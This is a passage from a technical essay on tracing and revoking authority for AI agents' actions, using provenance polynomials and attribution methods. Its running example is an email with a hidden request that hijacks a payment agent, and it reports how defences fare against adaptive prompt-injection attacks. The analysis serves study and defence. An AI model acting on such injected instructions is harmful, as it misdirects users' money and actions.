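Suppose S has already placed the 400-dollar payment in a queue at the bank when Alice withdraws her grant. Even if the company cancels the task, revokes S's credential and confirms that S's process has ended, the queued payment may still go through. Zhu and Wang designed their revocation protocol for this situation. It certifies that nothing can still act on a particular root grant, an original grant from which other permissions derive. They call this condition root-scoped quiescence.

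Counting Carol's approval as a root grant, the queued payment has two stored sets of sufficient grants, {a, c} and {b, c}. Suppose {a, c} is the one marked as selected. The protocol then works as follows:

1. **Retire the grant.** A central ledger marks Alice's grant as retired, after which nobody can use it to issue or extend a permission. The same transaction fixes the list of services to check and the list of messages in transit.
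2. **Find the affected tasks.** These are the tasks whose selected set contains a. A task that selected {b, c} can continue, even if {a, c} is one of its alternatives.
3. **Install fences.** Each service that carries out actions, such as the bank, starts rejecting requests that rely on Alice's grant. Any action it accepted before this point stands, and the service issues a receipt for it.
4. **Rebind or stop.** An affected task can continue only if it switches to another stored set that excludes a and whose grants are all current. The switch happens in one transaction and cannot change the task's operation or widen its effects. The queued payment could switch to {b, c}. If Carol had withdrawn instead, no set would remain, and the payment would have to stop.
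5. **Account for messages.** Every message sent under the old grant needs a matching record of acceptance, rejection or expiry. Otherwise two services could each report that they had nothing left to do while a payment request was travelling between them.
6. **Combine the reports.** A verifier checks the services' signed reports. It returns "quiescent" if nothing can still act on the grant, "not quiescent" if something can, and "indeterminate" if evidence is missing. A timeout never counts as success.

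The stored sets are minimal witnesses made up of root grants, although Zhu and Wang do not draw this connection. Their paper never mentions why-provenance or semirings, and none of its 39 references is about database provenance.

The protocol assumes that each task has a complete list of its sets, and evaluating the polynomial can produce that list. However, a permission with a small circuit can still have too many minimal sets to store one by one.

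Zhu and Wang ran 17 test cases, and all 17 matched the outcomes they had specified in advance. Some cases isolate the effect of the fence. When the controller only cancelled the task, the late action still went through in both runs. It also went through when the ledger retired the grant but the service had no fence. With a fence, the service rejected the action in all four runs, including one after a restart and one from a process that had opened the ledger before the withdrawal.

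A separately written checker agreed with all 17 results. It also rejected all 44 altered records. The researchers had changed the content of these records and then recalculated the digital fingerprints, so the changes could be detected only from what the records meant. These results are good evidence that the program follows its specification. They provide little evidence about deployment, because the tests used no outside services and the "actions" were inert entries in a local record.

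The safety proof rests on nine assumptions. They include that every action passes through a listed service with a working fence, that the list of services is complete, and that every task has recorded its minimal sets and its selection correctly. The services' records must also be authentic and survive crashes. Zhu and Wang add two more assumptions to guarantee that the process eventually finishes: services must respond and messages must arrive eventually. They also prove that if a service can be neither inspected nor fenced, no outside observer can always tell whether it still holds a delayed action, so the verdict has to be "indeterminate".

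Agents that modify their own software could regain a revoked grant by restoring an old copy of themselves. *Authorization for Self-Modifying AI Agent Populations* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) prevents this by treating each version of an agent as a new principal. A restored copy gets a new identity even if its files are identical to the old ones, and it does not recover revoked permissions or money already spent. When someone revokes a grant, every later version that depends on that grant also loses permission, unless it obtains an independent one.

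### The grant a task selected

The polynomial shows which grants could support the payment, and the mark on {a, c} identifies those the task is using. After Alice withdraws her grant, a new payment could rely on Bob's immediately, but the queued payment has to rebind first. Rebinding repeats the authorisation check and creates a receipt listing the old and new sets of grants, so an auditor can see that the payment went ahead on Bob's grant.

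Policies can also differ on whether a delegation depends on a particular grant. Under the company's rules, A's delegation to S is valid under either Alice's grant or Bob's. In the record system used in Choi and colleagues' tests, each delegation belongs permanently to one parent grant. If A had delegated to S under Alice's grant there, S's label would be acd alone, and Alice's withdrawal would stop S even though A could still act under Bob's grant.

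This stricter rule makes it clearer whose grant each delegation relied on, but it stops more work. The company's logical rules must match whichever policy its systems enforce. Otherwise, the polynomial could include bcd even though the payment service would refuse S.

### Payments made before the withdrawal

Suppose S paid V on Monday using Alice's grant, and Alice withdrew it on Tuesday. To check whether S may pay V on Wednesday, the company sets a to 0. Monday's payment is still authorised, because the grant was valid that day. To check that payment, the company should evaluate the polynomial with Monday's values, so it needs to keep the dates of grants and withdrawals. Zhu and Wang's revocation protocol likewise leaves completed actions in place. A refund would be a separate action that needs its own authorisation.

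A revocation can take effect at different times in different services. If Alice withdraws a grant at 10:00 and the bank installs its fence at 10:05, the bank might accept a payment at 10:03 even though the ledger has already retired the grant. The protocol requires a receipt showing that the bank accepted the payment before it installed the fence. Whether the company should treat that payment as authorised depends on its policy.

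The company does sometimes need to change a token's past value. If it discovers on Tuesday that someone forged Alice's grant, her token a should have been 0 on Monday. Monday's polynomial then becomes bcd, so Bob's grant would have permitted the payment, although the bank relied on the forged one. *Equivalence-Invariant Algebraic Provenance for Hyperplane Update Queries* (2020) applies the same idea to database changes by giving each transaction its own token. An analyst can then ask what the database would contain if a past transaction had never taken effect. For example, cancelling the mistaken withdrawal of a grant could make that grant reappear.

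These calculations change one thing and hold the rest fixed. *Putting Lipstick on Pig* (2012), which studies provenance in multi-step data processing, warns that the result of such a deletion may not match any actual run. Without Alice's grant, A might never have delegated to S, but the polynomial bcd is computed as if that delegation still happened.

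## The model's reasoning step and the assumptions it violates

Agent A delegated to sub-agent S because A's model requested the delegation, and S paid V because S's model requested the payment. The company's rules allowed both steps but do not explain why the models requested them. An auditor might try to extend the labels to cover those reasons by treating each model call as another query operator. The items in the context would be the inputs, each with its own token, and the requested action would be the output.

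The theorems about semiring labels rely on five assumptions about an operator:

- Its rules are known.
- It is monotone, so extra input never removes a result.
- It uses only the recorded inputs.
- It gives the same output whenever it receives the same input.
- Rewording a request without changing its meaning does not change the result.

A language model can violate all five.

### Testing the assumptions

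The known rules of joins and unions determine how their labels combine, but nobody can derive such a rule from a language model. Xu, Li and colleagues (2026) point out in *Sightline* that no code describes what happens inside a model call, so programs that track data usually assume either that nothing in the prompt reaches the output or that everything does. They took prompts from 2,103 families of open-source projects, filled the blanks with plausible values and ran the prompts on four models. Between 12% and 14% of the inserted values had no visible effect on the output, because the model ignored them, lacked the context to use them or refused the request. Whether a value affects the output depends on the other values and on what the model happens to write, so writing one rule for each prompt would not solve the problem.

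Ordinary, sensible behaviour can violate monotonicity. S might pay V after reading an overdue invoice, but not if it also reads a note that V has already received the money. Lin, Zeighami and Parameswaran measured how often extra text changes a model's answer to a question about a document in *Bolt-on, Verifiable Provenance for LLM-Powered Data Processing* (2026). They found a small set of sentences that gave the same answer as the whole document, then added other sentences back in 100 random combinations. The answer stayed the same in 88% to 94% of cases, depending on the model. The rate for current agents could be quite different, because the three models tested were older models from OpenAI and Google, and answering questions is simpler than choosing actions.

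Without monotonicity, an auditor learns less from finding a witness. For S, the invoice may be enough by itself but not together with the note. A minimal witness is also harder to find. For a monotone query, an auditor can find one by removing facts one at a time until every further removal would lose the result. With a model, the set left by this search may not be minimal, because removing two sentences together can preserve the answer even when removing either one alone would lose it. Lin and colleagues offer a proof that this cannot happen if, from any sufficient set, it is possible to add the remaining sentences one at a time without ever losing the answer. This condition is weaker than monotonicity and held in about 97% to 99% of their cases. The proof has a gap, because the path from a smaller sufficient set to the full text may bypass the set at which the search stopped.

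A model also draws on what it learned in training. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, test one design in which the two sources are separate. If x is the prompt, C the retrieved documents and y a possible answer, the probability of y is

```
p(y | x, C)  =  γ · p_documents(y | x, C)  +  (1 − γ) · p_model(y | x)
```

where γ is a number between 0 and 1. The second term does not contain C, so no document's token can account for it. In an ordinary model, the two sources are not even separate terms. One of the test conversations asks for the population of New York, and a model that learned the figure in training could answer without either of the two search results. In semiring terms, the answer's label would include the term 1, which stands for a fact that nobody tracks.

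*Putting Lipstick on Pig* gives a token to each row stored by software that remembers earlier inputs. This method does not work for training, because a model's weights are not a table with a row for each training document. A company could multiply every action's label by a token w for the model version. That would record which version chose the action, but not which part of its training influenced the choice.

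Repeated runs can also differ, because software usually picks each word at random according to the model's probabilities. S might pay in one run and ask for confirmation in the next. Setting the "temperature" to 0 makes the model always choose the most probable word, which should remove the randomness. Lin and colleagues ran each of their questions 50 times at this setting. On average, the most common wording accounted for 93% to 99% of the runs, and the most common meaning for 97% to 99.8%. They attribute the remaining differences to near-ties and to rounding in the hardware. Small differences add up over a long task. If each step had an independent 99% chance of matching an earlier run, all 40 steps of a task would match only about 67% of the time.

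Rewording is harder to test because someone has to decide whether two requests mean the same thing. Alice might write "settle V's invoice" or "make sure V gets paid", and only the second might lead S to pay before the invoice arrives. A side experiment by Lin and colleagues gives a rough idea of the effect's size. They asked models whether the sentences in each of 2,000 pairs had the same meaning, using a handwritten prompt and a version rewritten by a model. When both prompts included examples, GPT-5 was right 95.1% of the time with the handwritten prompt and 93.4% with the rewritten one, so it must have changed its answer on at least about 30 pairs. The rewritten prompt also defined "same meaning" in more detail and used other examples, so wording may not explain the whole difference.

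Order can also matter, although it doesn't affect the result of multiplication. Before testing part of a document, Lin and colleagues put the sentences back in their original order, because a different order might change the meaning.

### Deleting a token and running the step again

The practical consequence of these violations shows up in a simple test. Remove an input from the record by setting its token to 0, then remove it from the actual input and run the step again. For a query q on a table R, the theorem of Green and colleagues guarantees that the two results agree. For a model M with context C, nothing does:

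```
query:   q(R) with t set to 0            =   q(R without t)
model:   label of M(C) with t set to 0   ?   M(C without t)
```

Suppose V's invoice reaches S twice, as an attachment with the token x and as quoted text in an email with the token y. If either copy is enough for S to pay, the correct label is x + y, just as Alice's and Bob's grants gave a + b. The company knew how its rules combined the grants, but it has no such rule for the model. If the company multiplies the tokens instead, the label xy wrongly implies that S would not pay if either copy were missing.

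Rerunning the model without one copy is also misleading because S still pays, just as it does when Alice's and Bob's grants are tested one at a time. Xu and colleagues prove that this test always fails when the copies are interchangeable, and they confirmed the problem on four models. They scored each passage by how much removing it changed the probability of the recorded output. A single copy of the relevant text scored higher than an unrelated passage 93% to 97% of the time. With two extra copies, the figure fell to between 54% and 69%, where guessing would give 50%.

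Even a passage with nothing useful in it can change the output. Siddiqui and colleagues compared a model's answers from a full set of search results with its answers after they had removed results it did not seem to need. After the removal, the average overlap with a reference answer, where 1 is complete overlap, rose from 0.77 to 0.85 for a small model and from 0.82 to 0.90 for a larger one. In almost all the cases where their method chose the wrong label, the model had failed to answer properly from the full set, although they expected a robust model to ignore surplus text.

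A rerun can also produce an action that could not be predicted from the record. Without the invoice, S might pay another supplier or write to Alice for instructions, and the polynomial for the payment to V has no term for either action. A different result does not prove that the missing item mattered, since the output might have changed by chance.

### Multiplying every item into every action

A company that does not know which items the model used might decide to be cautious and treat them all as necessary. Suppose S has read 40 items before it pays V, with tokens x₁ to x₄₀. Only three affected its choice: the task instructions, the email m with the hidden request, and V's entry in the supplier register. The other 37 include a newsletter and a calendar invitation. The label for the payment would be

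```
x₁ · x₂ · x₃ · … · x₄₀
```

Setting any token to 0 makes the whole product 0. The label therefore falsely implies that S would not have paid V without the newsletter, and likewise for each of the other 36 irrelevant items. If S also sent a reminder and updated a spreadsheet after reading the 40 items, the labels of those actions would contain all these tokens too. An auditor could not tell from the labels that m led to the payment but had nothing to do with the spreadsheet.

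The exponents become meaningless even faster. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) defines an agent's context at each step as everything that came before it, including the model's own outputs and reasoning. Suppose S reads one new item before each response, and the host adds every response to the context. The labels are then:

```
response 1:   x₁
response 2:   x₁x₂ · (x₁)                =  x₁²x₂
response 3:   x₁x₂x₃ · (x₁) · (x₁²x₂)    =  x₁⁴x₂²x₃
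```

The exponent of x₁ doubles with each response and reaches 2³⁹, about 550 billion, by the fortieth. Unlike the squares in the faulty two-treasurer rule, these exponents count only the routes by which text could have returned to the context, not how often the model relied on it.

### Lineage as a list of possible influences

With lineage, the plain set {x₁, …, x₄₀}, the company makes a weaker claim that it can defend. If the auditor reads the set as "these items may have influenced the payment", it is accurate even though 37 of the items had no effect. It does not show whether any item was necessary, whether the three relevant ones were enough, or how they combined.

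The lineage set is useful mainly for ruling out documents. If a document is not in the set, its text did not reach the model through the context during this task. This holds only if the system records every input, including tool descriptions and searches that found nothing, since an empty result can also affect a decision. The record does not include what the model learned in training.

Security researchers have adopted the same cautious rule. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes a system in which each model response takes on the combined labels of all the messages and tool descriptions the model received. A single untrusted email therefore makes every later response untrusted while the email stays in the context. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) uses a similarly weak "candidate" link for evidence that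 may have contributed to a claim. It keeps this link separate from a link for support because a false note in an agent's memory can cause an action without justifying it.

Low attention does not prove that an item had no influence, so it is not a safe reason to drop the item from the list. Attention is the mechanism by which a model draws on earlier text, and Xu and colleagues prove that in a standard transformer a small change to an item cannot affect the output unless later text attends to it. But they also construct an example in which an item receives about two billionths of the total attention, and changing it still reverses the output. Any method for estimating influence therefore has to allow for some mistakes.

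Lineage becomes less useful for distinguishing actions as a task gets longer. Each action's lineage contains the lineage of every earlier action, so if S makes ten payments after reading m, m appears as a possible influence in the lineage of all ten. Near the end of a long task, the lineages of two consecutive actions might share hundreds of tokens and differ in one or two.

Summarizing the context does not shrink its lineage. When the context gets too long, the host may ask the model to condense, say, 40 items into a paragraph. Any of those items could have affected the paragraph, so its lineage contains all 40 provenance tokens, even if the original text is deleted.

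Stored memory carries the problem into later tasks. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, describe an agent that saves the details of an invoice on Monday and pays it on Tuesday. If the invoice contains an attacker's account number, the attack takes effect only on Tuesday. Their system therefore keeps each stored result's security label and restores it when a later request uses the result. Storing lineage in the same way would preserve the link to Monday's invoice. But if Monday's note summarised 40 items, every action that followed from it on Tuesday would inherit 40 tokens, and a note written on Tuesday would pass them on again. After a year of such notes, the lineage of each action could include nearly everything the agent had ever read.

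Siddiqui and colleagues use the established term "label creep" for this growth. It causes practical problems when a policy depends on the labels. One of their examples is a label that lists the people who must authorise an action. If S had read documents belonging to 40 people, cautious propagation would require all 40 to approve the payment.

Strict checks can also block work even when the labels are fairly precise. Girrens and Wang's system fixes a plan before it reads any outside data and tracks labels through the plan's steps. On AgentDojo, a standard set of tests for attacks on agents, none of the tested attacks succeeded with the label checks on, but the share of tasks completed fell from 53.0% to 29.0%. Girrens and Wang attribute the loss mainly to plans that use untrusted data for sensitive actions. Many legitimate tasks require such plans, such as paying an invoice that arrived by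 email, so better labels would not eliminate the whole loss.

### Coarse labels for the model and fine labels elsewhere

Much of an agent outside its model is ordinary software whose rules are known. *Putting Lipstick on Pig* combines components with known rules and opaque components in one provenance record. In its example, car dealers bid for a buyer's order. The record contains detailed provenance for the software that looks up and counts cars. The formula that sets the price is opaque, so the record connects its result to all of its inputs.

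The detailed part limits the imprecision caused by the opaque part. In the example, a dealer has one Honda Accord and two Honda Civics, and the buyer wants a Civic. A query selects the two Civics before the formula runs, so the bid's provenance includes them but not the Accord, even though nobody has looked inside the formula.

A company could use the same approach for S. If a query selected V's three unpaid invoices and the model saw only those, other suppliers' invoices would not appear in the payment's lineage. If ordinary code then copied the account number from the supplier register, the number would have only the register entry's token, while the decision to pay would depend on everything the model had read. Splitting a task into four model calls that each read ten items would give each result at most ten tokens instead of 40, as long as the calls did not read each other's output. The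 method requires a process without loops. An agent's cycle of model and tool calls meets that requirement once the task is over, because the record can list each call as a separate step.

The opaque steps still do not support predictions about deletion. *Putting Lipstick on Pig* removes a product from its record when any one factor is deleted, but it removes the result of an opaque function only when all the inputs are deleted. If a model had read 40 items, the payment would survive the deletion of any 39 of them under the rule for opaque functions, but deleting any one would remove it if the items were recorded as a product. Neither prediction is based on how the model behaves. The approach also helps little when a single model call reads everything and makes every decision, which is why some systems restrict what the model sees and does.

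### Dropping labels by running the model again

Siddiqui and colleagues found a way to shorten the lineage without relying on an estimate of influence. The system first runs the model on the full context, then checks how likely the model would have been to give the same output from a smaller set of documents with a less restrictive label, such as only the trusted ones. If the likelihood stays close enough, the system discards the first output, runs the model again on the smaller set and returns the new output with the new label.

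In the New York example, a trusted source gives the population as about 8.4 million and an untrusted one gives it as around 8 million. The trusted source is enough for the answer, so the system removes the other and reruns the model. The returned answer is correctly labeled "trusted" because the model's input on that run did not include the untrusted page. If the likelihood check is wrong, the second answer may be worse, but its label is still correct. The record passes the delete-and-rerun test for the removed documents because the system has performed that test.

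Siddiqui and colleagues tried this on 40 conversations with an agent, using Llama 2 models from 2023. A less restrictive label was possible in 20 of them, and the method found it in 17 with the smaller model and 19 with the larger one. It did worse on news articles, where it improved the label in 57% and 39% of the possible cases.

Another experiment comes close to recovering minimal witnesses from a model. Each document had its own label, and the questions asked for the personal details of invented people. For one question, document A covered the first person, and the second person's details were available either in D alone or in B and C together. The correct result was {A, B, C} and {A, D}, which correspond to the polynomial abc + ad. With 14 documents per question, there were 2¹⁴ = 16,384 possible sets. The method found exactly the correct sets for about 86% of the 64 questions. These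 were lookup questions with clear answers, and a decision to pay a supplier may not separate so clearly into alternatives.

The number of extra model calls can grow exponentially with the number of documents, but one comparison is enough if there are only two labels, such as "trusted" and "untrusted". An attacker can also add distracting text that keeps the system from finding a smaller set, so it has to keep the restrictive label. The rerun must happen before the agent acts. If S has already paid V, rerunning the model without m produces a new decision, but the payment still came from the old one.

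Xu and colleagues instead estimate which labels to drop without rerunning the model, and accept a small error rate. In tests on AgentDojo, their method removed half of the unnecessary labels while missing about 4% of the real influences. A security policy that used the remaining labels still blocked all 34 calls that would have carried out an attack. But the error rate is an average over many cases, so it does not guarantee that the label on any one payment is complete.

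### Why permission provenance survives

None of this affects the polynomial acd + bcd, provided that the permission check runs outside the model. The check can treat the model's output as one more fact, which records that S requested a payment of 400 dollars to V. If this fact has the token q, the label for the authorised payment is

```
(acd + bcd) · q
```

The policy engine applies known rules to recorded facts and gives the same answer each time, so the theorems hold for this calculation. If Alice withdraws her grant, setting a to 0 gives bcdq, and so does running the check again. The result doesn't depend on whether S had read three items or 40, or whether it would make the same request tomorrow, because the token q records only that the request happened.

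The company should keep q as a single token. If it replaced q with the product x₁ · x₂ · … · x₄₀, the label would again mark the payment as dependent on the newsletter, and an auditor could mistake the newsletter's sender for someone whose authority the payment needed. The lineage of the request belongs in a separate record that q points to.

Costa and colleagues also put their policy engine outside the model. It applies fixed rules to the labels on each proposed tool call to determine whether the call can go ahead. With suitable policies, it stopped every prompt injection in their tests. When they turned the checks off, practical attacks succeeded against all the designs they tested, including their own. The protection therefore depended on the engine's ability to block the model's tool calls.

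The separation fails if the company asks the model whether S may pay V, because the permission check then has all the weaknesses of a model call. It partly fails if a model supplies one of the facts. Suppose the policy allows payment only for goods that have arrived, and a model reads delivery emails and records, with the token g, that V's goods have arrived. The label (acd + bcd) · g · q correctly shows that the permission depends on g. But if one of the emails was forged, setting its token to 0 does not settle whether g should also become 0, so someone has to check whether the goods arrived.

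## Measuring what influenced an action

The lineage of S's request to pay V lists all 40 items that the model read. An auditor has to estimate which of them influenced the request, because no known rule connects a model's input to its output. Some methods change the input and run the model again, while others compare texts or use a second model to study the record. These methods measure different things, so two sound ones can give different results for the email m.

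### Text that is enough to reproduce an answer

Lin and colleagues define a counterpart to a witness for language models. Part of a text is a "verifiable provenance" of an answer if the same model, given the same question and only that part, produces an equivalent answer. If the wording differs, they use another model call to check whether the meaning is the same.

The whole text always qualifies, so the aim is to find a small part. There are two definitions of small enough:

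- A selection of sentences is **minimal** if removing any one sentence changes the answer.
- It is **strictly minimal** if no smaller selection from it gives the answer.

A minimal witness corresponds to a strictly minimal selection. A minimal selection may not be strictly minimal, because models are not always monotone. Suppose a text has four sentences, and the model gives the same answer from the whole text, from the first three sentences, and from the first sentence alone, but from no other selection. The first three sentences are minimal because no two of them are enough, but they are not strictly minimal because the first is enough alone.

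BLIP, the program that Lin and colleagues built, guarantees a minimal selection. It divides the text into 20 blocks, ranks them by similarity to the question and answer, and searches for a short list of top-ranked blocks that reproduces the answer. It then deletes sentences in growing batches, resetting the batch size to one whenever a deletion changes the answer, and stops when it can't delete any single remaining sentence without changing the answer.

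The main tests used 500 question-document pairs from each of five collections, including scientific papers, contracts and medical texts. The selections averaged between 3% and 11% of the text. Finding a selection took 4 to 10 seconds and cost 1.1 to 1.4 times as much as answering the question. Deleting sentences one at a time from a full scientific paper took over two hours and cost more than 100 times as much as answering the question.

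BLIP checks that each selection reproduces the answer before returning it, so the perfect score doesn't show that the model relied on those sentences when it read the whole text. In one example, the question is when a paper came out. The reference list cites a different paper from the same year, and that citation alone produces the right answer. Questions about tables give better evidence, because the correct rows are known. BLIP found exactly those rows for 96% to 100% of the questions, depending on the table and the difficulty.

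Sufficiency means less for a model's choice than for a permission. The policy allows the payment to V if any sufficient set of grants exists, so a witness fully justifies the payment. S, however, chose once, with all 40 items in its context. If the invoice alone would lead S to pay, and m alone would too, both are verifiable provenances of the payment, but neither result shows which one S acted on.

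### Replaying a step without outside instructions

*AttriGuard* (He, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) presents a test of whether the user's request or outside content caused a tool call. The system of the same name runs the test before each call:

1. The agent proposes a call in the usual way.
2. A model rewrites everything the agent's tools have returned. It turns structured data into prose and commands into reports, and it weakens claims that an action is necessary. For example, a direct order to send a report turns into a remark that the text asks for this.
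3. The agent's model chooses again, using the rewritten material and the record of its real earlier actions.
4. If the same call appears, the original goes ahead. If the tool is the same but the arguments differ, another model judges whether the call still fits the user's task. Otherwise, AttriGuard blocks the call.

Step 3 keeps the earlier actions fixed because two separate runs could differ for reasons unrelated to the rewriting. If the instruction to pay V came only from m, S should not make the payment in the replay. But if Alice had asked S to settle V's invoice, S should still pay, since the rewritten invoice still contains the payee and the amount.

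The quantity behind the test is the "control effect" of the outside content on a call:

```
log p(call | original content)  −  log p(call | rewritten content)
```

Suppose S requests the payment in 90% of runs with the original content and in 3% with the rewritten content. The control effect is log(0.90/0.03), or about 3.4. These probabilities usually aren't available for commercial models, so AttriGuard replays the step once and checks whether the call appears. In this example, the payment call would still appear in 3% of replays.

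He et al. tested four models on 882 attacks from AgentDojo and 400 from another benchmark. With the defence, none of the standard attacks succeeded, but the agents completed about 3% fewer ordinary tasks and the amount of model text roughly doubled. When attackers knew the defence and optimised their text against it, 6.6% of attacks succeeded with Gemini 2.5, compared with 29.5% to 82.0% for competing defences in the same test.

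These figures measure how well AttriGuard blocks attacks, so they are only indirect evidence of how accurately it identifies causes. The tests also left out tasks in which the user lets outside content decide everything, such as "Complete the to-do list in this file." A request to pay whatever invoices arrive by email is similar, and both a real invoice and a forged one could appear to be what the user wanted paid.

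### Changing only the stated source

An auditor may also want to know whether the source of a statement affects a model's actions. Liao, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Auditing Provenance Sensitivity in LLM Agent Action Selection*, tested this with 450 short tasks. They added one statement to each prompt and marked it either trusted and current or untrusted and external, without changing its words or position. Some statements supported the correct action and others proposed an alternative, such as cancelling an order instead of exchanging an item.

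Across five open-weight models, switching a statement's mark between trusted and untrusted changed the chosen tool or argument in 5.4% of cases when the statement proposed an alternative to the correct action, and in 1.7% when it supported the correct action. When the statement proposed an alternative, marking it as untrusted corrected 4.0% of the choices and made 1.2% incorrect. The models' error rate was 6.7% without the added statement, 9.5% with an untrusted alternative and 12.2% with a trusted one, so they gave less weight to untrusted statements but did not ignore them completely.

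This measurement is clean because only one thing changes between the two prompts. However, it shows how susceptible a model is on average, not whether m prompted this payment. The mark was only text in the prompt, so the result also doesn't show whether models can recognise the origin of a real email.

The same tasks show how one item can hide the influence of another. In one, a user authorises two bags on a flight, while an old preference in the context says four. One model booked two. When the researchers removed the user's current instruction, it booked four, and when they also removed the old preference, it went back to two. Removing only the old preference from the full context would have suggested that it had no influence. Liao and colleagues found this pattern, in which a correct choice turns wrong and then correct again, in 2.4% of 12,120 comparisons. They built the tasks to contain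 conflicting information, so the rate in ordinary use could be quite different.

### Two emails that are each enough

Suppose S reads a second email, n, with the same hidden request as m. Either email is enough to make S pay V, and without both of them S would not pay:

| Emails in the context | Does S pay V? |
|---|---|
| m and n | Yes |
| Only m | Yes |
| Only n | Yes |
| Neither | No |

As with the two copies of V's invoice, a test that removes one item at a time shows no influence from either email, although S would not have paid without at least one of them. Philosophers call this overdetermination, meaning that an outcome has more than one sufficient cause. An attacker can create it by sending the same message twice.

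The polynomial m + n records both causes, but the auditor can write it only after learning what S does in each row of the table. Each row requires at least one run, and more if the model's choices vary.

Liao and colleagues ran this kind of complete test on tasks with eight items, which have 2⁸ = 256 combinations. For each combination Z, they calculated a score v(Z) for how strongly the model favoured a given tool or argument. They then calculated an "interaction" for each group of items B, which is the part of the score that smaller groups within B do not explain:

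```
I(B) = sum over every Z contained in B of  (−1)^(|B| − |Z|) · v(Z)
```

Here |B| and |Z| are the numbers of items in each group. If the score is 1 when S pays and 0 when it doesn't, the two emails give:

```
I(m)        =  1 − 0          =   1
I(n)        =  1 − 0          =   1
I(m and n)  =  1 − 1 − 1 + 0  =  −1
```

The negative interaction shows that the emails duplicate each other. If S needed both emails before it would pay, the results would be different:

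| Measure | Either email is enough | S needs both |
|---|---|---|
| Effect of removing m alone | 0 | 1 |
| Effect of removing n alone | 0 | 1 |
| Interactions for m, n and the pair | 1, 1, −1 | 0, 0, 1 |
| Shapley value of each email | ½ | ½ |
| Polynomial | m + n | mn |

An item's Shapley value is the average effect of adding it, taken over every order in which the items could be added. Unlike the removal test, it gives each email some credit, but the credit is the same in both columns. A single number for each item therefore cannot show whether the items were alternatives or worked together, but the interactions and the polynomial can.

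With real models, the interactions were less informative than in this example. Those involving unauthorised items were slightly stronger than chance when averaged over incomplete contexts, but not near the full context. The difference reversed when the researchers compared these items with others that proposed competing actions in the same way. A simple difference in scores predicted which actions would change better than a measure based on interactions did, ranking a changed case above an unchanged one 85% of the time, compared with 81%. The method also requires access to the model's word probabilities.

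The number of reruns in a complete test doubles with each item, so S's 40 items would require more than a trillion. Removing one or two items at a time takes only 820 reruns and would reveal that m and n are alternatives. But an attacker could send a third copy, and finding three interchangeable emails would take up to 10,700 reruns.

Removing a whole group at once takes less computation. AttriGuard rewrites all outside content together, so n cannot mask the influence of m. If the agent no longer makes the payment, the auditor knows that outside content prompted it and can search for the particular emails. BLIP's search would return m or n, depending on which it reached first. A slower version looks for several selections and might return both, though it isn't guaranteed to find them all. Looking for five selections increased the computation from about 1.3 to 1.8 times that of the original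 answer.

A user's request can still hide an attack from AttriGuard. If Alice had asked S to pay V, the payment would still occur in the replay, even though m was also enough to cause it. That may be the right result for deciding whether to allow the payment, but it is less useful for investigating who tried to hijack the agent.

### Asking about one part of an action

S's decision to pay and the account number it used may come from different sources. An auditor who asks only "what influenced this payment?" could get either one as the answer. *Auditing Agent Actions Through Query-Conditioned Attribution* (Liu, Venkateswaran and colleagues, 2026) makes the auditor's question part of the method's input. In the paper's example, an airline agent cancels a reservation. The airline's policy and the customer's confirmation explain the choice to cancel, while the reservation number comes from the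 customer's original request.

The method uses a small open-weight model to study the record, so it doesn't need access to the model that acted. The method first writes an alternative to the real action that leaves out the part in question, such as proceeding without settling on an account number. It then gives the small model the history and has it choose between the real action and the alternative. A gradient calculation measures how sensitive this choice is to each piece of the history. The method gives extra weight to text that resembles the auditor's question and ranks the steps in the history by their total scores.

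The ranking takes two to three seconds for each question. Removing one step at a time with the same small models took 10 to 13 seconds, because it needed about 41 runs on average.

To test the method, Liu and colleagues built A³Bench, a set of 1,396 questions about which policy a recorded agent action relied on, where an argument came from, how a failure spread or what led to unsafe behaviour. On the 1,041 questions in the main test, three small models placed the correct source first in 38%, 57% and 54% of cases. For the model that scored 38%, removing one step at a time worked better, at 45%. A system that combined all three models and used another to settle disagreements scored 64.5%, compared with 60.4% for the best large commercial model that read the record directly.

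More than a third of the combined system's answers were therefore wrong. Each test question has exactly one correct source, so the benchmark doesn't cover cases like m and n. Wang and colleagues surveyed research on agent traces and found no benchmark in their catalogue that tests a complete chain of provenance.

Liu and colleagues describe the result as an action's basis in the visible record, not as a cause inside the acting model. This difference matters little for an account number that appears in only one document, but it matters more for the decision to pay, because several documents could offer a plausible reason even though only some of them affected the model.

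### Matching words to their sources

*LMLineage* (Hou, Geng and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that runs beside an agent and compares the agent's output with its input. For each output sentence, the system searches every input document for the passage closest in meaning and attributes the sentence to the document containing that passage. If the similarity is 0.72, the system assigns 72% of the sentence to that document and 28% to the model's own knowledge.

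These percentages are a convention and don't measure what the model used. In tests with two models, the system's confidence in its choice of source differed from its accuracy by about 45 percentage points on average.

The main test used ten questions in Chinese, with web pages as source material. The system had to decide whether each sentence in an answer came from the user's prompt, a web page or the model itself. It was right for 66% to 79% of the sentences, depending on which of three models wrote the answers. Hou and colleagues labelled a fourth model's answers and used those labels for the other three, so these figures depend on how closely the three models' answers match the fourth's. In longer sessions of 3 to 40 turns, accuracy was between 55% and 63%.

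Choosing one passage from each document first was faster and more accurate than comparing each output sentence with every input sentence. A web page could have thousands of sentences and the user's prompt only two or three, so when every sentence was compared, the best match often came from the web page by chance. Choosing one passage per document reduced this bias. This method took about a second per turn in the longer sessions on a GPU, but one large job on a CPU took 168 seconds.

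Text matching could help an auditor find where S got V's account number. But if the invoice and m both contain that number, matching cannot show which one S used. Matching can also miss an instruction whose words don't appear in the output. For example, a line in m that said "do not ask Alice first" could stop S from asking for confirmation, even if nothing in the payment request resembled that line.

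### The model's written reasoning

Many models write out their reasoning before they act. S might write, "V's invoice is overdue, so I will pay it." This is easier to read than any of the records above, but it is model output and may leave out what influenced the action.

Explanations that a model gives afterwards are especially weak evidence because, as He and colleagues warn, a hijacked model can invent a justification for what it has done. Lin and colleagues asked three older models, GPT-4o mini, GPT-4o and Gemini 2 Flash, to list the sentences that contributed to their answers. Given only those sentences, the models reproduced their answers in about 65%, 74% and 53% of cases, respectively. Many of the lists were therefore not enough to produce the answer, though they could still have included sentences that mattered.

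Reasoning written before an action can be better evidence of what influenced it than an explanation written afterward, because the reasoning becomes part of the context and can affect what the model does next. It may still be incomplete, since the model has its whole context when it chooses the action, and an item can affect the choice without appearing in the reasoning.

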